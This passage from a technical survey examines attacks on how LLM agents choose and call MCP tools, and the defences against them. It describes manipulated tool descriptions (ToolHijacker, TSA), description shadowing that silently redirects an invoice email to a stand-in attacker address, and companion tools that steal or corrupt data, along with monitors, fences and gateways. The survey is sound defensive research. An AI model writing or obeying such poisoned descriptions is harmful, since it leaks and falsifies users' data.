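|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tagged copy | 48.2% | 37.6% | 42.6% | 2.57 |
| GAPMA | 43.3% | 34.0% | 36.2% | 3.90 |
| AMA | 73.1% | 71.6% | 67.4% | 3.81 |
| ToolHijacker | 75.2% | 74.5% | 80.9% | 2.68 |
| TSA | 88.7% | 80.1% | 92.1% | 4.00 |
| Genuine description | – | – | – | 4.03 |

The search did not use GPT-5, so TSA's 92.1% success rate on that model shows that a description developed on one model can work on another. With 20 tools, TSA's success rate on GPT-5 was still 85.1%. Its lowest result on any model not used in the search was 73.1%, for Qwen3.8-27B on MetaTool with 20 tools. On MCP-Atlas, whose tasks each need three to six calls, TSA reached 80.1%.

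Competing genuine tools reduced TSA's success only moderately. The model chose the false tool for 79.1% of requests when two genuine tools could answer them, and for 75.9% when three could. An attacker can also register more than one false tool. With three false tools and one genuine tool, the model chose a false one for 95.0% of requests. When the model could choose among the genuine description and all five false ones for the same function, it chose TSA's for 50.4% of requests.

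The human ranking is weaker evidence than the success rates. Five people, from a pool of twenty recruited online, ranked each set of descriptions. They found the tagged copies and ToolHijacker's descriptions significantly more suspicious than the genuine ones, but found no significant difference for TSA's. The genuine descriptions averaged only 4.03, not far above the 3.5 expected from random ranking, so the participants could not reliably recognise an honest description, although they could recognise crude manipulation. An experienced reviewer who knows what the tool is supposed to do might do better.

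GPT-5 and Qwen3.8-27B are the newest models in these studies, and TSA succeeded about 75% of the time on Qwen3.8-27B. None of the studies tested Claude Fable 5.2, GPT-6.2 Astra or Gemini 4, so those models' resistance has to be measured separately. Attack success was higher on GPT-5 than on the older Llama 3.3, which is a reason not to assume that a more capable model will resist.

### Comparison with an exact copy

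A model with no preference between a genuine tool and an exact copy would pick each half the time. If a malicious tool is picked 48% of the time against one genuine tool, its wording may therefore have had no effect. Dai and colleagues report no test with an exact copy, but their other measurements allow an estimate of how often one would be picked. Without an attack, Llama 3.3 picked the correct tool for 81.7% of TSABench requests. If a copy were picked for half of those, its share would be about 41% of all requests. The same calculation gives about 46% for Llama 3.3 on MetaTool and for GPT-5 on TSABench.

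By this standard, the tagged copy and GAPMA had little or no effect in most of the tests. On Llama 3.3, the tagged copy won 48.2% on TSABench and 44.6% on MetaTool, while GAPMA won 43.3% on TSABench and 45.4% on MetaTool. Most of the percentages correspond to whole numbers out of 141 requests, so differences of a few points could easily be due to chance. However, the tagged copy had a clear effect on GPT-5 with MetaTool, where it won 76.6%. TSA and ToolHijacker were far above the estimate on both collections. AMA was well above it on TSABench but won only 53.9% on MetaTool.

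The comparison also makes TSA's results against several genuine tools more impressive. An exact copy would receive, on average, at most a third of requests against two genuine tools and at most a quarter against three. TSA received 75.9% against three, about three times the copy's share.

The order in which tools are listed complicates any such estimate. When Faghih and colleagues gave GPT-4.1 two identical tools, it correctly used the first in 80.2% of cases and the second in 13.6%. Qwen2.5-7B used the first in 76.7% and never used the second. Even an exact copy could therefore look like a powerful attack if it were listed first, and listing a real attack second could hide its effect. Faghih and colleagues avoided this problem by listing each edited tool first in half the tests.

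Even when researchers balance the order, equivalent tools don't receive equal shares. Blankenstein, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *BiasBusters*, gave seven models groups of five interchangeable tools and rotated the order so that each tool came first once per request. They measured the distance between the actual shares P_i and equal shares of 1/K for K tools:

```
δ = ½ · Σ |P_i − 1/K|,   i = 1 to K
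```

A value of 0.3 means that 30% of the choices would have to move to other tools to make the shares equal. The models averaged between 0.25 and 0.37, with no attacker involved. The best predictor of a tool's share was how closely its description matched the request in meaning.

This undermines the baseline that Wang and colleagues used for GAPMA. They assumed that, without manipulation, each of six servers would win a sixth of the requests, or 16.7%. GPT-4o's 22.2% is only slightly higher and depends on a few extreme cases. Of the 32 combinations of style and function, 18 never won a request and five won all ten, accounting for 50 of the 71 successes. The other four models' results are too high to dismiss this way, but without a measured baseline nobody can say how much of them comes from the wording.

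Dai and colleagues repeated part of the GAPMA experiment and concluded that their version did better than the original. The comparison is doubtful because they describe using the authoritative style, but the original figures they list match those for the exaggerated style, which was much weaker on Claude. Their average for Claude is slightly lower than the original average for the authoritative style, although they also used a newer Claude model. Their GPT-4o result, 62.5% over four functions, is higher than the original result for either style, which suggests that GAPMA's results vary a lot between runs.

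ToolHijacker's retrieval part plainly describes what the tool does, so testing it alone gives something close to a neutral baseline. With only this part, the model chose the malicious tool for 5% of requests. An equal share would have been around 20%, since each MetaTool task has four or five genuine tools. Adding the selection part raised the rate to 99%, so the wording clearly caused the increase, though the test covered only one task and one model.

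Mo and colleagues compared tool definitions refined by repeated search with attractive ones that a language model wrote without it. In the informed tests, the definitions written without the search succeeded in 72% to 90% of cases, and the search added 4 to 12 percentage points. Attackers can evidently get most of the benefit with very little effort. The comparison doesn't show how often the agents would have called a plainly described tool.

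### Trained models, filters and scanners

Some defences train the model to ignore instructions in untrusted text. StruQ separates the trusted prompt from the data and trains the model to follow only the prompt. SecAlign trains the model on pairs of safe and unsafe answers to text containing injected instructions. Shi and colleagues tested both defences against the gradient-free version of ToolHijacker. They measured attack success rates of 99.7% on MetaTool and 92.7% on ToolBench for the StruQ model, and 96.7% and 90.4% for the SecAlign model.

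These defences target commands, but a model that ignores every command still has to rely on the rest of the description. If the description falsely presents `find_records` as the more reliable source of invoices, the model can reasonably choose it.

Mo and colleagues tried two defences that need no training. The first rewrites the user's request to remove injected content, which made little difference to AMA because the hostile text is in the tool definition. The second adds a rule to the system prompt to reject suspicious tools. It lowered attack success by less than 7 points when the attacker knew the field of work. When the attacker didn't, it lowered success by 19 points for Llama 3.3 and 22 for Gemma 3, but both models still called the false tool in more than half the cases. The rule is easy to add but shouldn't be the main protection.

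Perplexity filters look for unnatural text. Shi and colleagues set the threshold on genuine descriptions, aiming to flag at most about 1% of them. The basic filter missed all the malicious descriptions produced without gradients, seven each for MetaTool and ToolBench. A version that examines short stretches of text missed six of the seven on MetaTool and all seven on ToolBench. The filters caught a few more of the gradient-based descriptions, which read less naturally. Such filters are even less promising against TSA, because its search already selects for low perplexity.

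*Known-answer detection* places a simple instruction in front of the suspect text and checks whether the model still carries it out. If the model doesn't, the text has probably diverted it. This method missed every ToolHijacker description.

Scanners built for MCP servers combine keyword rules with other checks, in some cases including a language model. Dai and colleagues tested three of them, along with two detectors that rely on a prompted language model. The detection rates on TSABench were:

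| Detector | Tagged copy | GAPMA | AMA | ToolHijacker | TSA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| MCP-Scanner | 100% | 0% | 0% | 2.1% | 0% |
| MCP-Shield | 100% | 0% | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| MCP-Guard | 100% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| GAPMA's own detector | 4.3% | 0% | 0% | 8.5% | 4.3% |
| General language-model detector | 90.1% | 0.1% | 0% | 85.3% | 0% |

A scanner that finds every tagged copy can therefore miss every TSA description. The general detector is useful against ToolHijacker, which the MCP scanners mostly missed. Dai and colleagues report a highest detection rate of 4.25% for TSA, but that applies only to TSABench, since MCP-Guard detected 6.4% on MetaTool.

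TSA's low detection rates also depend on when the search stops. The paper states that its experiments stopped the search after three successes in a row. Elsewhere, it reports that the general detector caught 54% of the descriptions produced with that setting, and that a setting of seven worked best. The 54% figure conflicts with the table, where the same detector caught none. Most likely, the paper misstates the setting it used, but TSA's reputation for being undetectable depends partly on that setting.

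Stricter detectors create false alarms. Dai and colleagues found that PromptLocate, which looks for injected instructions, flagged every genuine tool description as malicious, probably because descriptions normally tell a model when and how to use a tool. When Wang and colleagues asked five language models to judge descriptions, the models flagged 10% of the untouched ones but no more than 5% of those written by GAPMA, so their warnings were almost useless for telling whether a description was honest.

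Shen and colleagues recommend removing commands from tool definitions and filtering out text that could bias the choice of tool. Removing commands would weaken ToolHijacker, but biasing text is much harder to filter out, because a TSA description may contain only a plausible account of the tool and some mild praise. Hu and colleagues also warn that attackers can adapt their descriptions to evade text-based detectors.

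A person who approves each call faces the same difficulty. Cline, a coding agent, shows the server's name, the tool and its description before a call. A TSA description would not stand out there the way an order to always choose the tool would. The approver should check the server's identity first, because an invoice request does not belong on the notes server, however good the description sounds.

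### Taking the choice away from publishers

The operator of an AI system can replace the publishers' descriptions with its own. The client then gives the model the operator's text and keeps the publisher's text out of the context. In the office assistant, two of the definitions might change like this:

| Tool | Publisher's description | Operator's description |
|---|---|---|
| `get_invoice` | Gets an invoice by number. | Returns an invoice from the company's accounts. Use this tool for all invoice requests. |
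| `find_records` | A dependable way to look up invoices and payments. | Searches the text of meeting notes. |

In Faghih and colleagues' tests, wording that asserted priority had the strongest effect on models' choice of tool, and the operator can use the same kind of wording to favour a trusted tool. When replacing a publisher's description, the operator should also replace the tool's name, title and parameter descriptions, because the publisher can put persuasive text in any of them. If a language model drafts the new text, it needs other information besides the old description, or it may repeat the false claims in different words.

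None of the attack studies measured how well rewriting tool descriptions works as a defence. The evidence for it is indirect. In several of the studies, changing only the description changed the model's choice. Some preference may remain after rewriting, because Blankenstein and colleagues found that descriptions did not fully explain the models' choices and that training on text about one tool increased a model's preference for that tool's provider. Rewriting also takes work for every tool and every update, and it doesn't change what the tool's code does after a call.

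For sensitive tasks, *fixed routing* is stronger because the model no longer chooses between publishers. The operator decides in advance which tool handles each task:

```
look up an invoice   →  accounts server, get_invoice
send an email        →  mail server, send_email
anything else        →  the model chooses
```

For the request "find invoice 1042 and send it to Dana", the client would offer the model only `get_invoice` and `send_email`. The model never receives the description of `find_records`, so its wording has no effect. The rule that recognises the task must not use the tools' descriptions, or the attacker could influence that step instead. The rule can be a list of keywords, a button in the application or a separate classifier that receives only the user's request.

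Fixed routing fails when a request doesn't match the rule. A user who asks "what do we still owe the printers?" wants an invoice but doesn't use the word. If that request falls through to the open choice, `find_records` becomes a candidate again. The client can reduce this risk by offering only trusted tools when the rule gives no clear match, and by making third-party tools available only when the user clearly asks for them. These limits make the assistant less flexible, which is reasonable for payments and email but probably not for looking up the weather.

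Disabling a rival tool, as the office could do with the notes server's `send_email`, is simpler still where nobody needs the tool. This helps because it removes the untrusted tool, not because it shortens the list. When Dai and colleagues cut the list from 10 tools to 5 but left the false tool in it, TSA's success rate on TSABench rose slightly, from 88.7% to 90.1%. Adding harmless tools is no solution either. It lowered the attack's success rate somewhat, but Llama 3.3's accuracy without any attack also fell, from 81.7% with 10 tools to 62.5% with 40.

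Blankenstein and colleagues propose selecting the relevant tools, then picking one at random. This achieves their aim of reducing unfair preferences between honest providers. It is unsuitable for protecting invoices, because one false tool beside one genuine tool would still receive half the requests, and three false tools would receive three quarters. Protecting invoices requires excluding untrustworthy tools from the choice.

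### Agents that claim every task

The same weakness exists where AI agents pass work to each other. In the Agent2Agent protocol, which Google introduced in 2025, each agent publishes an *agent card* describing its abilities. A coordinating agent can give these cards to a language model and ask it which agent should get a task. The security company Trustwave showed in 2025 that an attacker who controls one agent can exaggerate the abilities on its card so that the coordinator sends it every task. The attacker then receives the users' data and can return false results.

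Using an agent card to claim every task is a broader attack than ToolHijacker or TSA, which target one task at a time. The attacker receives more data, but the attack is easier to notice because the other agents stop receiving tasks. A card that exaggerates only one ability would be harder to spot.

Suppose the office assistant delegates bookkeeping to one agent and scheduling to another. The operator can write its own summary of each agent and use a fixed route for bookkeeping, just as it would for tools. The coordinator would then use the operator's list to decide which agent gets the work, and the agent's published card for technical details such as its address.

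## Tools that alter calls to other tools, and how to isolate them

A model can pick the right tool and still call it with the wrong arguments. With description shadowing, the office assistant could use the company's genuine `send_email` for every message and still send invoice 1042 to a stranger.

### How one description changes another tool's call

In Invariant Labs' April 2025 experiment with Cursor, the adding tool's description used an invented technical problem to justify sending all emails to one address. It included a false assurance that the real recipient's address would still be found in the message, a warning that the application would crash if emails went anywhere else, and an instruction not to tell the user.

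In the office assistant, the same attack would work like this:

1. The client loads the definitions from all three servers. In the description of `search_notes`, the notes developer has written that all invoices must go to an "archive" address, which the developer controls.
2. The model calls `get_invoice` with the number 1042, and the accounts server returns the invoice.
3. The model calls `send_email` with the archive address as the recipient.
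4. The client looks up `send_email` and correctly sends the call to the mail server.
5. The mail server emails the invoice from the user's own account and returns a confirmation.
6. The model tells the user that it has sent the invoice to Dana.

The call that the user wanted and the call that the client sent differ in one argument:

```
Wanted:  mail / send_email   to: Dana                    body: invoice 1042
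Sent:    mail / send_email   to: archive@notes.example   body: invoice 1042
```

The notes server never receives a call. The model calls the correct tool on the correct server, and the archive address is valid, so neither prefixes nor a check against the tool's schema would stop the call. In the interaction log from Invariant Labs' experiment, the changed recipient appeared only in the call's arguments.

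MCP gives each server its own connection to the client, so the notes server can't send anything to the mail server directly. *Jumping the line* (2025), by the security company Trail of Bits, explains that this separation isn't enough because all the descriptions share one context, so the model can act on one server's text when it uses another server's tools. The company tested a description that contained false information about the user's operating system. It led the clients and models tested, including Claude Desktop, to add an extra command to every shell command. The extra command let every account on the computer read and write to the user's home directory.

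In a system with a retriever, a shadowing description affects the model only if the retriever selects it. With the invented similarity scores used earlier for the invoice request, the retriever adds `search_notes` to the context but not `create_note`. The attacker would therefore put the false rule in the description of `search_notes`, or of every tool on the server.

Shen and colleagues list some less noticeable variants. One adds a `bcc` parameter to the call, so Dana receives the invoice and the attacker gets a copy. The assistant's `send_email` has only `to` and `body` parameters, so a mail server that rejects unlisted parameters would stop this, although the attacker could try to get two addresses into `to`. Another variant puts the false information in a tool's reply instead of its description. The reply to a notes search in the morning may still be in the context when the user asks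 for the invoice in the afternoon.

Neither Invariant Labs nor Trail of Bits reports a success rate. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* covers more clients, testing seven in November 2025. In the most relevant test, a tool's description claimed the tool had to run before any tool on another server. When called, it recorded which tool the user needed and what the user had asked for. Cursor called it automatically, Claude Desktop and Langflow were partly vulnerable, and Cline, Continue, Gemini CLI and Claude Code resisted the attack. Cursor ran several models on its default setting, while most of the others ran Claude Sonnet 4.5, so the result doesn't show whether the failure came from Cursor or its models.

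### Tools that insert themselves into a task

An attacker can also interfere with a trusted tool by getting a malicious tool to run just before or after it. *Les Dissonances*, a study that Li, Cui and colleagues presented at the NDSS security conference in February 2026, calls this *cross-tool harvesting and polluting*. Harvesting means collecting the data that other tools use or produce, and polluting means corrupting it.

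The malicious tool's description says it helps with using the trusted tool, which leads the agent to call it. For example, a Yahoo Finance tool for company news needs a stock symbol such as AAPL, but users usually give the company's name. The researchers added a tool described as converting names to symbols, and the agent called it before the news tool, even though the agent's model, GPT-4o-mini, could supply the symbols and use the news tool without help. In their conference talk, Li and colleagues attribute such behaviour to models' tendency to call tools instead of using their own knowledge, and to rely on descriptions of code they can't inspect.

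The researchers also got agents to call malicious tools by describing them as helpful in many other ways. They presented some as tools for formatting search terms correctly, validating data or explaining error messages, and others as tools for improving security. Agents called a supposed detector of harmful prompts at the start of their tasks, and a supposed checker of database queries before running each query.

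A malicious tool can collect data, such as the user's net worth, by listing it as a parameter, as in Mo and colleagues' tests. A malicious tool that runs before a trusted tool can corrupt the trusted tool's input. In one test run, the agent asked for Netflix's share price, but the malicious tool replaced Netflix's stock symbol with Nike's. A malicious tool that runs afterwards can corrupt the result. One presented as a validator of financial data raised share prices by 10%.

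In the office assistant, the notes developer could offer a tool called `format_invoice`, described as preparing invoices for email:

```
get_invoice(1042)  →  format_invoice(invoice)  →  send_email(to: Dana, body: formatted invoice)
```

The notes developer receives the whole invoice and can return it with a different bank account number. The email still goes to Dana, so checking the recipient doesn't reveal the change.

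To measure how common the problem is, the researchers built a program called Chord. For each trusted tool, Chord has GPT-4o write malicious companions, one to run before it and one to run after it, and tries each companion on five requests. The researchers tested 37 tools from LangChain and 29 from LlamaIndex, two frameworks for building agents. The tools included search engines, financial data services and travel services. Adding up the results for the two frameworks gives these totals out of 66 tools:

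| Position of the malicious tool | Agent called it | It collected data | It corrupted data |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the trusted tool | 47 | 45 | 35 |
| After the trusted tool | 35 | 31 | 25 |
| Either position | 50 | 48 | 45 |

The attack therefore worked in some form on about three quarters of the tools. The figures for collecting and corrupting data, 72% and 68%, are shares of all 66 tools, although the study's introduction describes them as shares of the 50 hijacked tools.

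The researchers counted a tool as vulnerable if the attack succeeded in at least one of five rounds. This is a lenient test, since an attack that works 13% of the time would pass it about half the time. But companions that ran before the trusted tool did much better. For the typical hijacked tool in either framework, the agent called the companion in all five rounds. Corrupting data was less reliable and succeeded in two or more rounds for about half of the affected tools.

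A tool can work as its developers intended and still count as "vulnerable" in this study, as Yahoo's news tool did. The weakness there was the agent's readiness to call the companion. The sample also leaves out tools that require payment or a complicated setup, so the proportion may not hold for all the tools in the two collections.

The stock symbol converter ran almost every time a request named the company, but only about half the time across all the test requests, because many already contained the symbol. Developers of trusted tools can make such converters less likely to run by accepting information in the form that users give it. For example, `get_invoice` accepts a plain invoice number and `send_email` accepts a name, so neither obviously needs a converter.

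The researchers also tried the LangChain companions on two other models. Agents running GPT-4o called 75% of the companions designed to run first, compared with 58% for GPT-OSS-120B and 26% for Llama 4 Scout. Li and colleagues conclude that models with stronger reasoning are more susceptible because they better understand how the companion relates to the trusted tool. But the companions were developed with GPT-4o, which could also explain its higher rate, and all three models are more than a year old.

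### Defences that the companions got past

Li and colleagues tested four existing defences on ten of the hijacked tools. The table shows how often the agent called the malicious companion:

| Defence | What it does | Companion before the tool | Companion after the tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | 78% | 73% |
| AirGap | Removes unnecessary data from arguments | 66% | 74% |
| Tool filter | Removes tools that the request doesn't need | 67% | 57% |
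| Spotlighting | Marks tools' replies as data, not instructions | 60% | 79% |
| Injection detector | Scans tools' replies for hidden instructions | 77% | 76% |

The success rate for collecting data was 46% to 49% without a defence and 40% to 61% with one. Each percentage comes from at most 50 attempts, so most of the differences could be due to chance.

Spotlighting and the injection detector failed because they guard against instructions in tools' replies, and the companions' replies contained only plausible data. AirGap failed because the companions requested data that suited the task.

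The researchers also attacked two systems that isolate tools from each other. IsolateGPT runs each tool in a separate compartment, but a language model first reads every tool's description and plans which tools to use. The researchers described a malicious tool as adding tax and tips to a taxi fare, and the model included it in the plan in all ten rounds. Separate compartments don't protect data that the plan itself passes to the attacker.

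ACE, the other system, first writes a plan from the user's request without looking at the available tools. It then matches each step to the tool with the most similar description. Selection manipulation is still possible at this later stage. When the researchers gave a malicious tool a description closer to the planned step than the genuine tool's, ACE always chose the malicious tool.

### The email attack in a formal model

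An appendix to Dongol's November 2026 paper applies its proofs to a simplified version of Invariant Labs' email attack, although tool poisoning is outside the paper's main scope.

The analysis compares two agents that follow the same plan with the same permissions. The real agent may obey instructions in untrusted text, while the *reference agent* never does. An agent *leaks* the difference between two possible secrets, such as an invoice for £400 and one for £900, if the attacker supplies the same text in both cases but observes different results. The real agent is secure if it leaks only differences that the reference agent also leaks, though perhaps in response to different text.

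With the false archive rule in its context, the real agent sends the attacker an email that shows £400 or £900. The reference agent emails only Dana, so the attacker sees nothing in either case, and the real agent is therefore insecure. The comparison is useful because many agents disclose information on purpose. If an agent sends its user's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting, an injected instruction that obtains the same calendar doesn't count as a new leak.

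Dongol then adds a *monitor*, a program that can refuse calls, and a *fence*, a rule that withdraws certain tools as soon as the agent reads untrusted text. The agent reads the malicious server's descriptions before anything else, so the fence takes effect at the start of the session. In terms of the office assistant, the results are:

| Tools withdrawn | Result |
|---|---|
| None | The invoice reaches the attacker |
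| Only the notes server's tools | The invoice still reaches the attacker |
| Every tool except sending to Dana | The attacker receives nothing |

Removing only the notes server's tools doesn't stop the attack, because once the false rule is in the context, the harmful call goes to the mail server.

The stricter fence works because nothing that the false rule asks for is still available. Dongol proves this for every plan that uses these tools and for a wide range of model behaviour. The proof assumes that each injected instruction causes a single call, that no injected instruction sends another email to Dana, and that the moment when the model obeys doesn't depend on the secret. The surrounding software must also meet several conditions:

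- An ordinary program, rather than the model, carries out a plan fixed in advance.
- Every tool call and every piece of untrusted text passes through the monitor.
- The attacker can't see which calls the monitor refuses, for example in an error message.
- A fresh session clears everything that the model has kept from untrusted text.
- The attacker can't edit sources that the system trusts, such as the address book.

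In the proof, each recipient has a separate sending tool, so the fence can leave "send to Dana" available and withdraw the others. The real `send_email` takes the recipient as an argument, so the practical equivalent is a rule that allows the call only when `to` contains Dana's address.

In Invariant Labs' experiment, the model both planned the email and wrote the altered call. The fence would block that call, so Dana would not receive the email, which is inconvenient but better than leaking the invoice.

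The analysis covers only leaks. If a false description leads the assistant to send Dana an invoice with the wrong bank account number, the attacker learns nothing, and the assistant still meets the definition of security. An assistant that can't make any calls also meets it, so anyone who installs a fence should test separately that the assistant can still do its work.

### Keeping untrusted text away from sensitive tools

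An operator can isolate the notes server with six measures. They have different effects on description shadowing, where the recipient changes, and on an inserted tool such as `format_invoice`:

| Measure | Changed recipient | Inserted tool |
|---|---|---|
| Load only the tools a task needs | Prevents it if no notes tool is loaded | Prevents it if no notes tool is loaded |
| Use separate sessions | Prevents it | Prevents it |
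| Plan before reading untrusted descriptions | Prevents it if the plan fixes the recipient | Prevents it if the plan fixes the tools |
| Check arguments against the request | Prevents it | Only if the check covers the body |
| Give each server its own credentials | Limits the damage | Limits the damage |
| Permit only listed tools at a gateway | Only if the gateway checks arguments | Prevents it |

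The simplest measure is to load only the tools that a task needs, as fixed routing does. If the notes server's definitions aren't loaded, the model never receives the false archive rule. However, someone has to decide which tools belong to each kind of task, and a wrong decision leaves the assistant without a tool it needs.

A fixed list or the user's selection should determine which tools are available for a task. Li and colleagues tested a filter in which a language model selected tools by reading their descriptions. It removed many malicious tools, but in one case it also removed the search engine that the task needed. Attackers could get past the filter by claiming in their tool's description that the tool was necessary.

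Many applications load more servers than they need. Rostamzadeh and colleagues describe a "configure once, run always" approach in which applications relaunch every registered server at each startup without asking the user again. If a user installed the notes server for one meeting in March, its descriptions may still be in the context in December. Trail of Bits advises users to disable any server they aren't actively using.

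Separate sessions are a stricter version of the same idea. The office could have one kind of session for mail and accounts and another for notes, with no way to combine them. This is less convenient, because a user who wants to email a meeting note has to copy it from one session to the other. The copied text is also untrusted, so users should copy only the passage they need and check it first.

Disconnecting the notes server halfway through a conversation is not enough, because its text may still be in the context. In Dongol's example, an agent regains permission to send messages while an attacker's earlier email is still in its context, and then leaks a new report. The client should start a fresh session before making sensitive tools available again.

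Even a new session may contain malicious instructions if the assistant has long-term memory. Dongol also models SpAIware, a reported attack in which a web page or document made ChatGPT store an instruction in its memory. ChatGPT then loaded the instruction into later conversations and leaked the user's messages. An assistant for sensitive work should therefore share no memory with the notes sessions, or treat that memory as untrusted. The drawback is that it forgets preferences and earlier work.

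If a task really needs both trusted and untrusted tools, the assistant can make its plan before the untrusted descriptions enter the context. Given only the user's request and the trusted definitions, the model might write this plan:

```
invoice = accounts / get_invoice(1042)
          mail / send_email(to: Dana, body: invoice)
```

An ordinary program then carries out the plan. A tool description that arrives later can't change the recipient or add `format_invoice`. IsolateGPT also planned first, but its planner read the malicious description, so planning first does not prevent the attack by itself. If the plan needs a notes tool, the operator should supply that tool's description and decide in advance which tool performs each step, because an attacker could exploit ACE's automatic matching of tools to steps.

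Planning first makes the assistant less flexible. It works for finding and sending an invoice, but not for a request such as "read Dana's message and do what she asks", where the next step depends on the message. The operator could allow such requests only in sessions without sensitive tools, or ask the user to approve each new step.

### Restricting what each call can do

The client can also check the arguments of a call just before sending it. For the invoice request, it would look up Dana in the company's address book and compare her address with the `to` argument. The archive address doesn't match, so the client would stop the call regardless of what changed the address.

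The check needs a reliable way to find the recipient in the request. If the client uses a language model for this, that model should receive only the user's words, not tool definitions or earlier replies. The notes server must also be unable to edit the address book, or the notes developer could replace Dana's address there and pass the check.

This check is easy when the request names one person, but for "Send it to the usual people", the client would have to ask who they are. Checking the recipient also doesn't protect the contents of the email. The safest way to protect an invoice is for the client to copy it directly from the accounts server's reply into the email, so that neither the model nor another tool can change it. The assistant then can't shorten or reword the invoice, but that is a minor drawback.

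An agent restricted to a list of permitted arguments can still leak a little information. In one of Dongol's examples, an agent is allowed to fetch only a newsletter's web address. An attacker's instruction makes it fetch the newsletter if a secret is 0 and try to fetch a forbidden address otherwise. An attacker who can tell whether the agent fetched the newsletter learns whether the secret is 0. This matters less for the office assistant, because the notes developer can't normally see whether Dana has received an email.

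Separate credentials limit what a malicious server can do with a stolen password or access token. The accounts server should have a token that can only read invoices, and the mail server should have one that can only send mail. The notes server should have neither. Invariant Labs warns that a malicious server can cause the model to pass one server's credentials to another. The client should therefore give each server its token directly and keep all tokens out of the model's context and out of files that the model can read.

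A notes server that runs on the user's own computer may be able to read those files without the model's help. Running it in a container, with access only to its own files and approved network addresses, prevents this. The main drawback is administrative work, because someone has to issue, renew and withdraw several tokens and maintain the container. Neither measure prevents description shadowing, since the mail server sends the altered email with its own valid token. A mail token that allows only internal recipients would block email to the archive address, but also to customers.

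A *gateway* is a program between the client and the servers that refuses any call its rules don't allow. For the invoice task, the rules might be:

```
accounts / get_invoice    only if the number is 1042
mail     / send_email     only if the recipient is Dana's address
anything else             refuse
```

A list of permitted servers and tools keeps `format_invoice` from running even if its description has led the model to call it. The list doesn't stop the altered email, because `send_email` on the mail server is a permitted tool. The gateway therefore also needs the rule about the recipient, and the client has to pass on the details of the user's request in a form that the model can't change.

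A gateway protects only the calls that go through it. If the client starts some servers directly, or the assistant can run shell commands with open network access, the model can get around it. Dongol's proof likewise requires every call to pass through the monitor. The gateway also adds a short delay to each call and is one more program to maintain. If it fails, it should refuse calls, so the assistant stops working until someone repairs it.

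For the office assistant, it makes sense to first leave the notes server out of invoice sessions and check the recipient of every email. Neither step requires a new model or a redesign of the assistant. A gateway becomes more worthwhile when several assistants use the same servers, because the administrator can then maintain the rules in one place.

### How much user confirmation adds

A confirmation prompt can help the user stop the altered email if it shows the real recipient. The user asked for an email to Dana, so an unfamiliar archive address should stand out. The prompt has to show the arguments the client is about to send, not the model's summary of them, because the summary may still list Dana as the recipient.

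Some confirmation prompts make this difficult. When Cursor leaked login keys in Invariant Labs' other experiment, its confirmation dialog hid the keys even in the extended view. Tests of seven clients found that Claude Desktop and Cline show all the arguments, but users have to scroll sideways to read long ones. The same study also gives Cline its top rating for showing arguments clearly, which is inconsistent with that finding. A prompt for `send_email` should show the full address without scrolling.

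People may also approve calls out of habit or without understanding them. Trail of Bits notes that many coding assistants let users turn off confirmation for commands, and that people often use assistants for tasks they know little about, which makes a harmful addition hard to spot. Li and colleagues raise a similar objection to IsolateGPT, which asks the user's permission before one tool uses another's data. They argue that a malicious companion tool requests data that suits the task, so the request looks reasonable. Neither group measured how often people notice a harmful call, so the benefit of confirmation is uncertain.

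The scope of the user's approval also matters. Dongol analyses an agent whose user approves the next use of a sending tool, whatever its arguments. An injected call can use up that approval to send private data, and the monitor then blocks the user's own message. If the approval covers the exact recipient and text, an injected call gets through only when it is identical to the approved one. An attacker who can measure when messages arrive may still learn something, because an identical injected call arrives slightly earlier than the planned one would.

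Frequent prompts encourage people to click without reading. The client can instead ask only when an automatic check fails or can't decide. It would ask about a new address, a payment or a deletion, but not about an email to Dana that matches the request. The prompt could then show the mismatch, for example: "You asked to email Dana, but this message is addressed to archive@notes.example."

Confirmation is much less useful against `format_invoice`. The prompt shows the correct recipient and what looks like the correct invoice, and few users know which bank account number belongs on it.

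## Earlier cases in browser extensions, voice assistants and chatbot plugins

The makers of browsers, phones and voice assistants accepted add-ons from outside developers long before MCP existed, and they had to decide which add-on should receive each request. OpenAI faced the same problem in 2023 with the first ChatGPT plugins. Browsers and phones match requests against fixed rules, and voice assistants match them by sound. ChatGPT picked plugins by their descriptions, much as the office assistant picks tools.

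### How browsers choose between two extensions

A browser extension is a small program that adds a feature to a web browser, such as blocking advertisements. Many extensions work on the requests that the browser sends when it loads pages, images and scripts. An extension lists the addresses that interest it. It can then block a matching request, redirect it to another address, or change its *headers*, the technical information that accompanies it. Two extensions may try to do different things to the same request, so browsers need rules for conflicts:

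| Conflict | Chrome | Firefox |
|---|---|---|
| One extension blocks a request and another redirects it | Blocking wins | Blocking wins |
| Two extensions redirect the same request with their own code | The most recently installed one wins | No fixed order; it depends on which registers first |
| Two extensions replace the page shown in a new tab | The last one wins | The most recent one to ask wins, since Firefox 56 |

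Chrome's rules for requests appear in Google's *chrome.webRequest*. Firefox's appear in Mozilla's *[DNR] Choose a deterministic extension prioritization order that makes sense*, a discussion among the browser's developers. The Firefox rule for new tabs comes from a change that mattw requested in *Use the pref manager to handle precedence for extensions using chrome_url_overrides*. yfdyh000 later asked, in *Choose UI to chrome_url_overrides*, for a menu where users could choose, and quoted documentation that still described the first extension as winning in Firefox. Written precedence rules can evidently lag behind the software, so they are worth testing.

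Giving priority to blocking is cautious, because the worst result is a page that fails to load. A gateway for the office assistant can work the same way and hold back a call if the call fails any check. The drawback is that a hostile extension can block requests the user wants.

Chrome's preference for the most recently installed extension is predictable, and it suits a user who has just installed something and expects it to work. It also helps an attacker, whose extension only has to be installed last. The developer of the overridden extension may not notice. Google writes that Chrome doesn't tell an extension when it ignores a redirect, although the same page describes an event, available since Chrome 70, that reports ignored redirects.

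Firefox's developers considered ranking extensions by their latest update. One objected that an extension could then gain priority just by publishing an update, and that users could not control the order. An MCP client that lets the latest tool list replace earlier entries has the same flaw.

Google later restricted what extensions can do to requests. Under Manifest V3, the current format for Chrome extensions, only extensions that an organization installs by policy can make the browser wait while their own code decides what to do with a request. Other extensions give the browser a list of rules to apply, such as "block scripts from example.com". According to *declarativeNetRequest*, Mozilla's Firefox documentation for these rules, this improves privacy because extensions don't read the requests. An extension can block requests without permission for specific sites, but it needs permission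 for the sites involved to redirect requests or change their headers.

When rules from different extensions conflict, blocking takes priority, then redirecting, then allowing. Chrome still breaks ties in favor of the most recently installed extension. Firefox also prevents one extension's rules from affecting another extension's requests. Mozilla's *[DNR] Prevent DNR from affecting requests from other extensions by default* records a discussion in which the general view was that extensions aren't expected to alter each other's requests. The office assistant has no such barrier between its servers.

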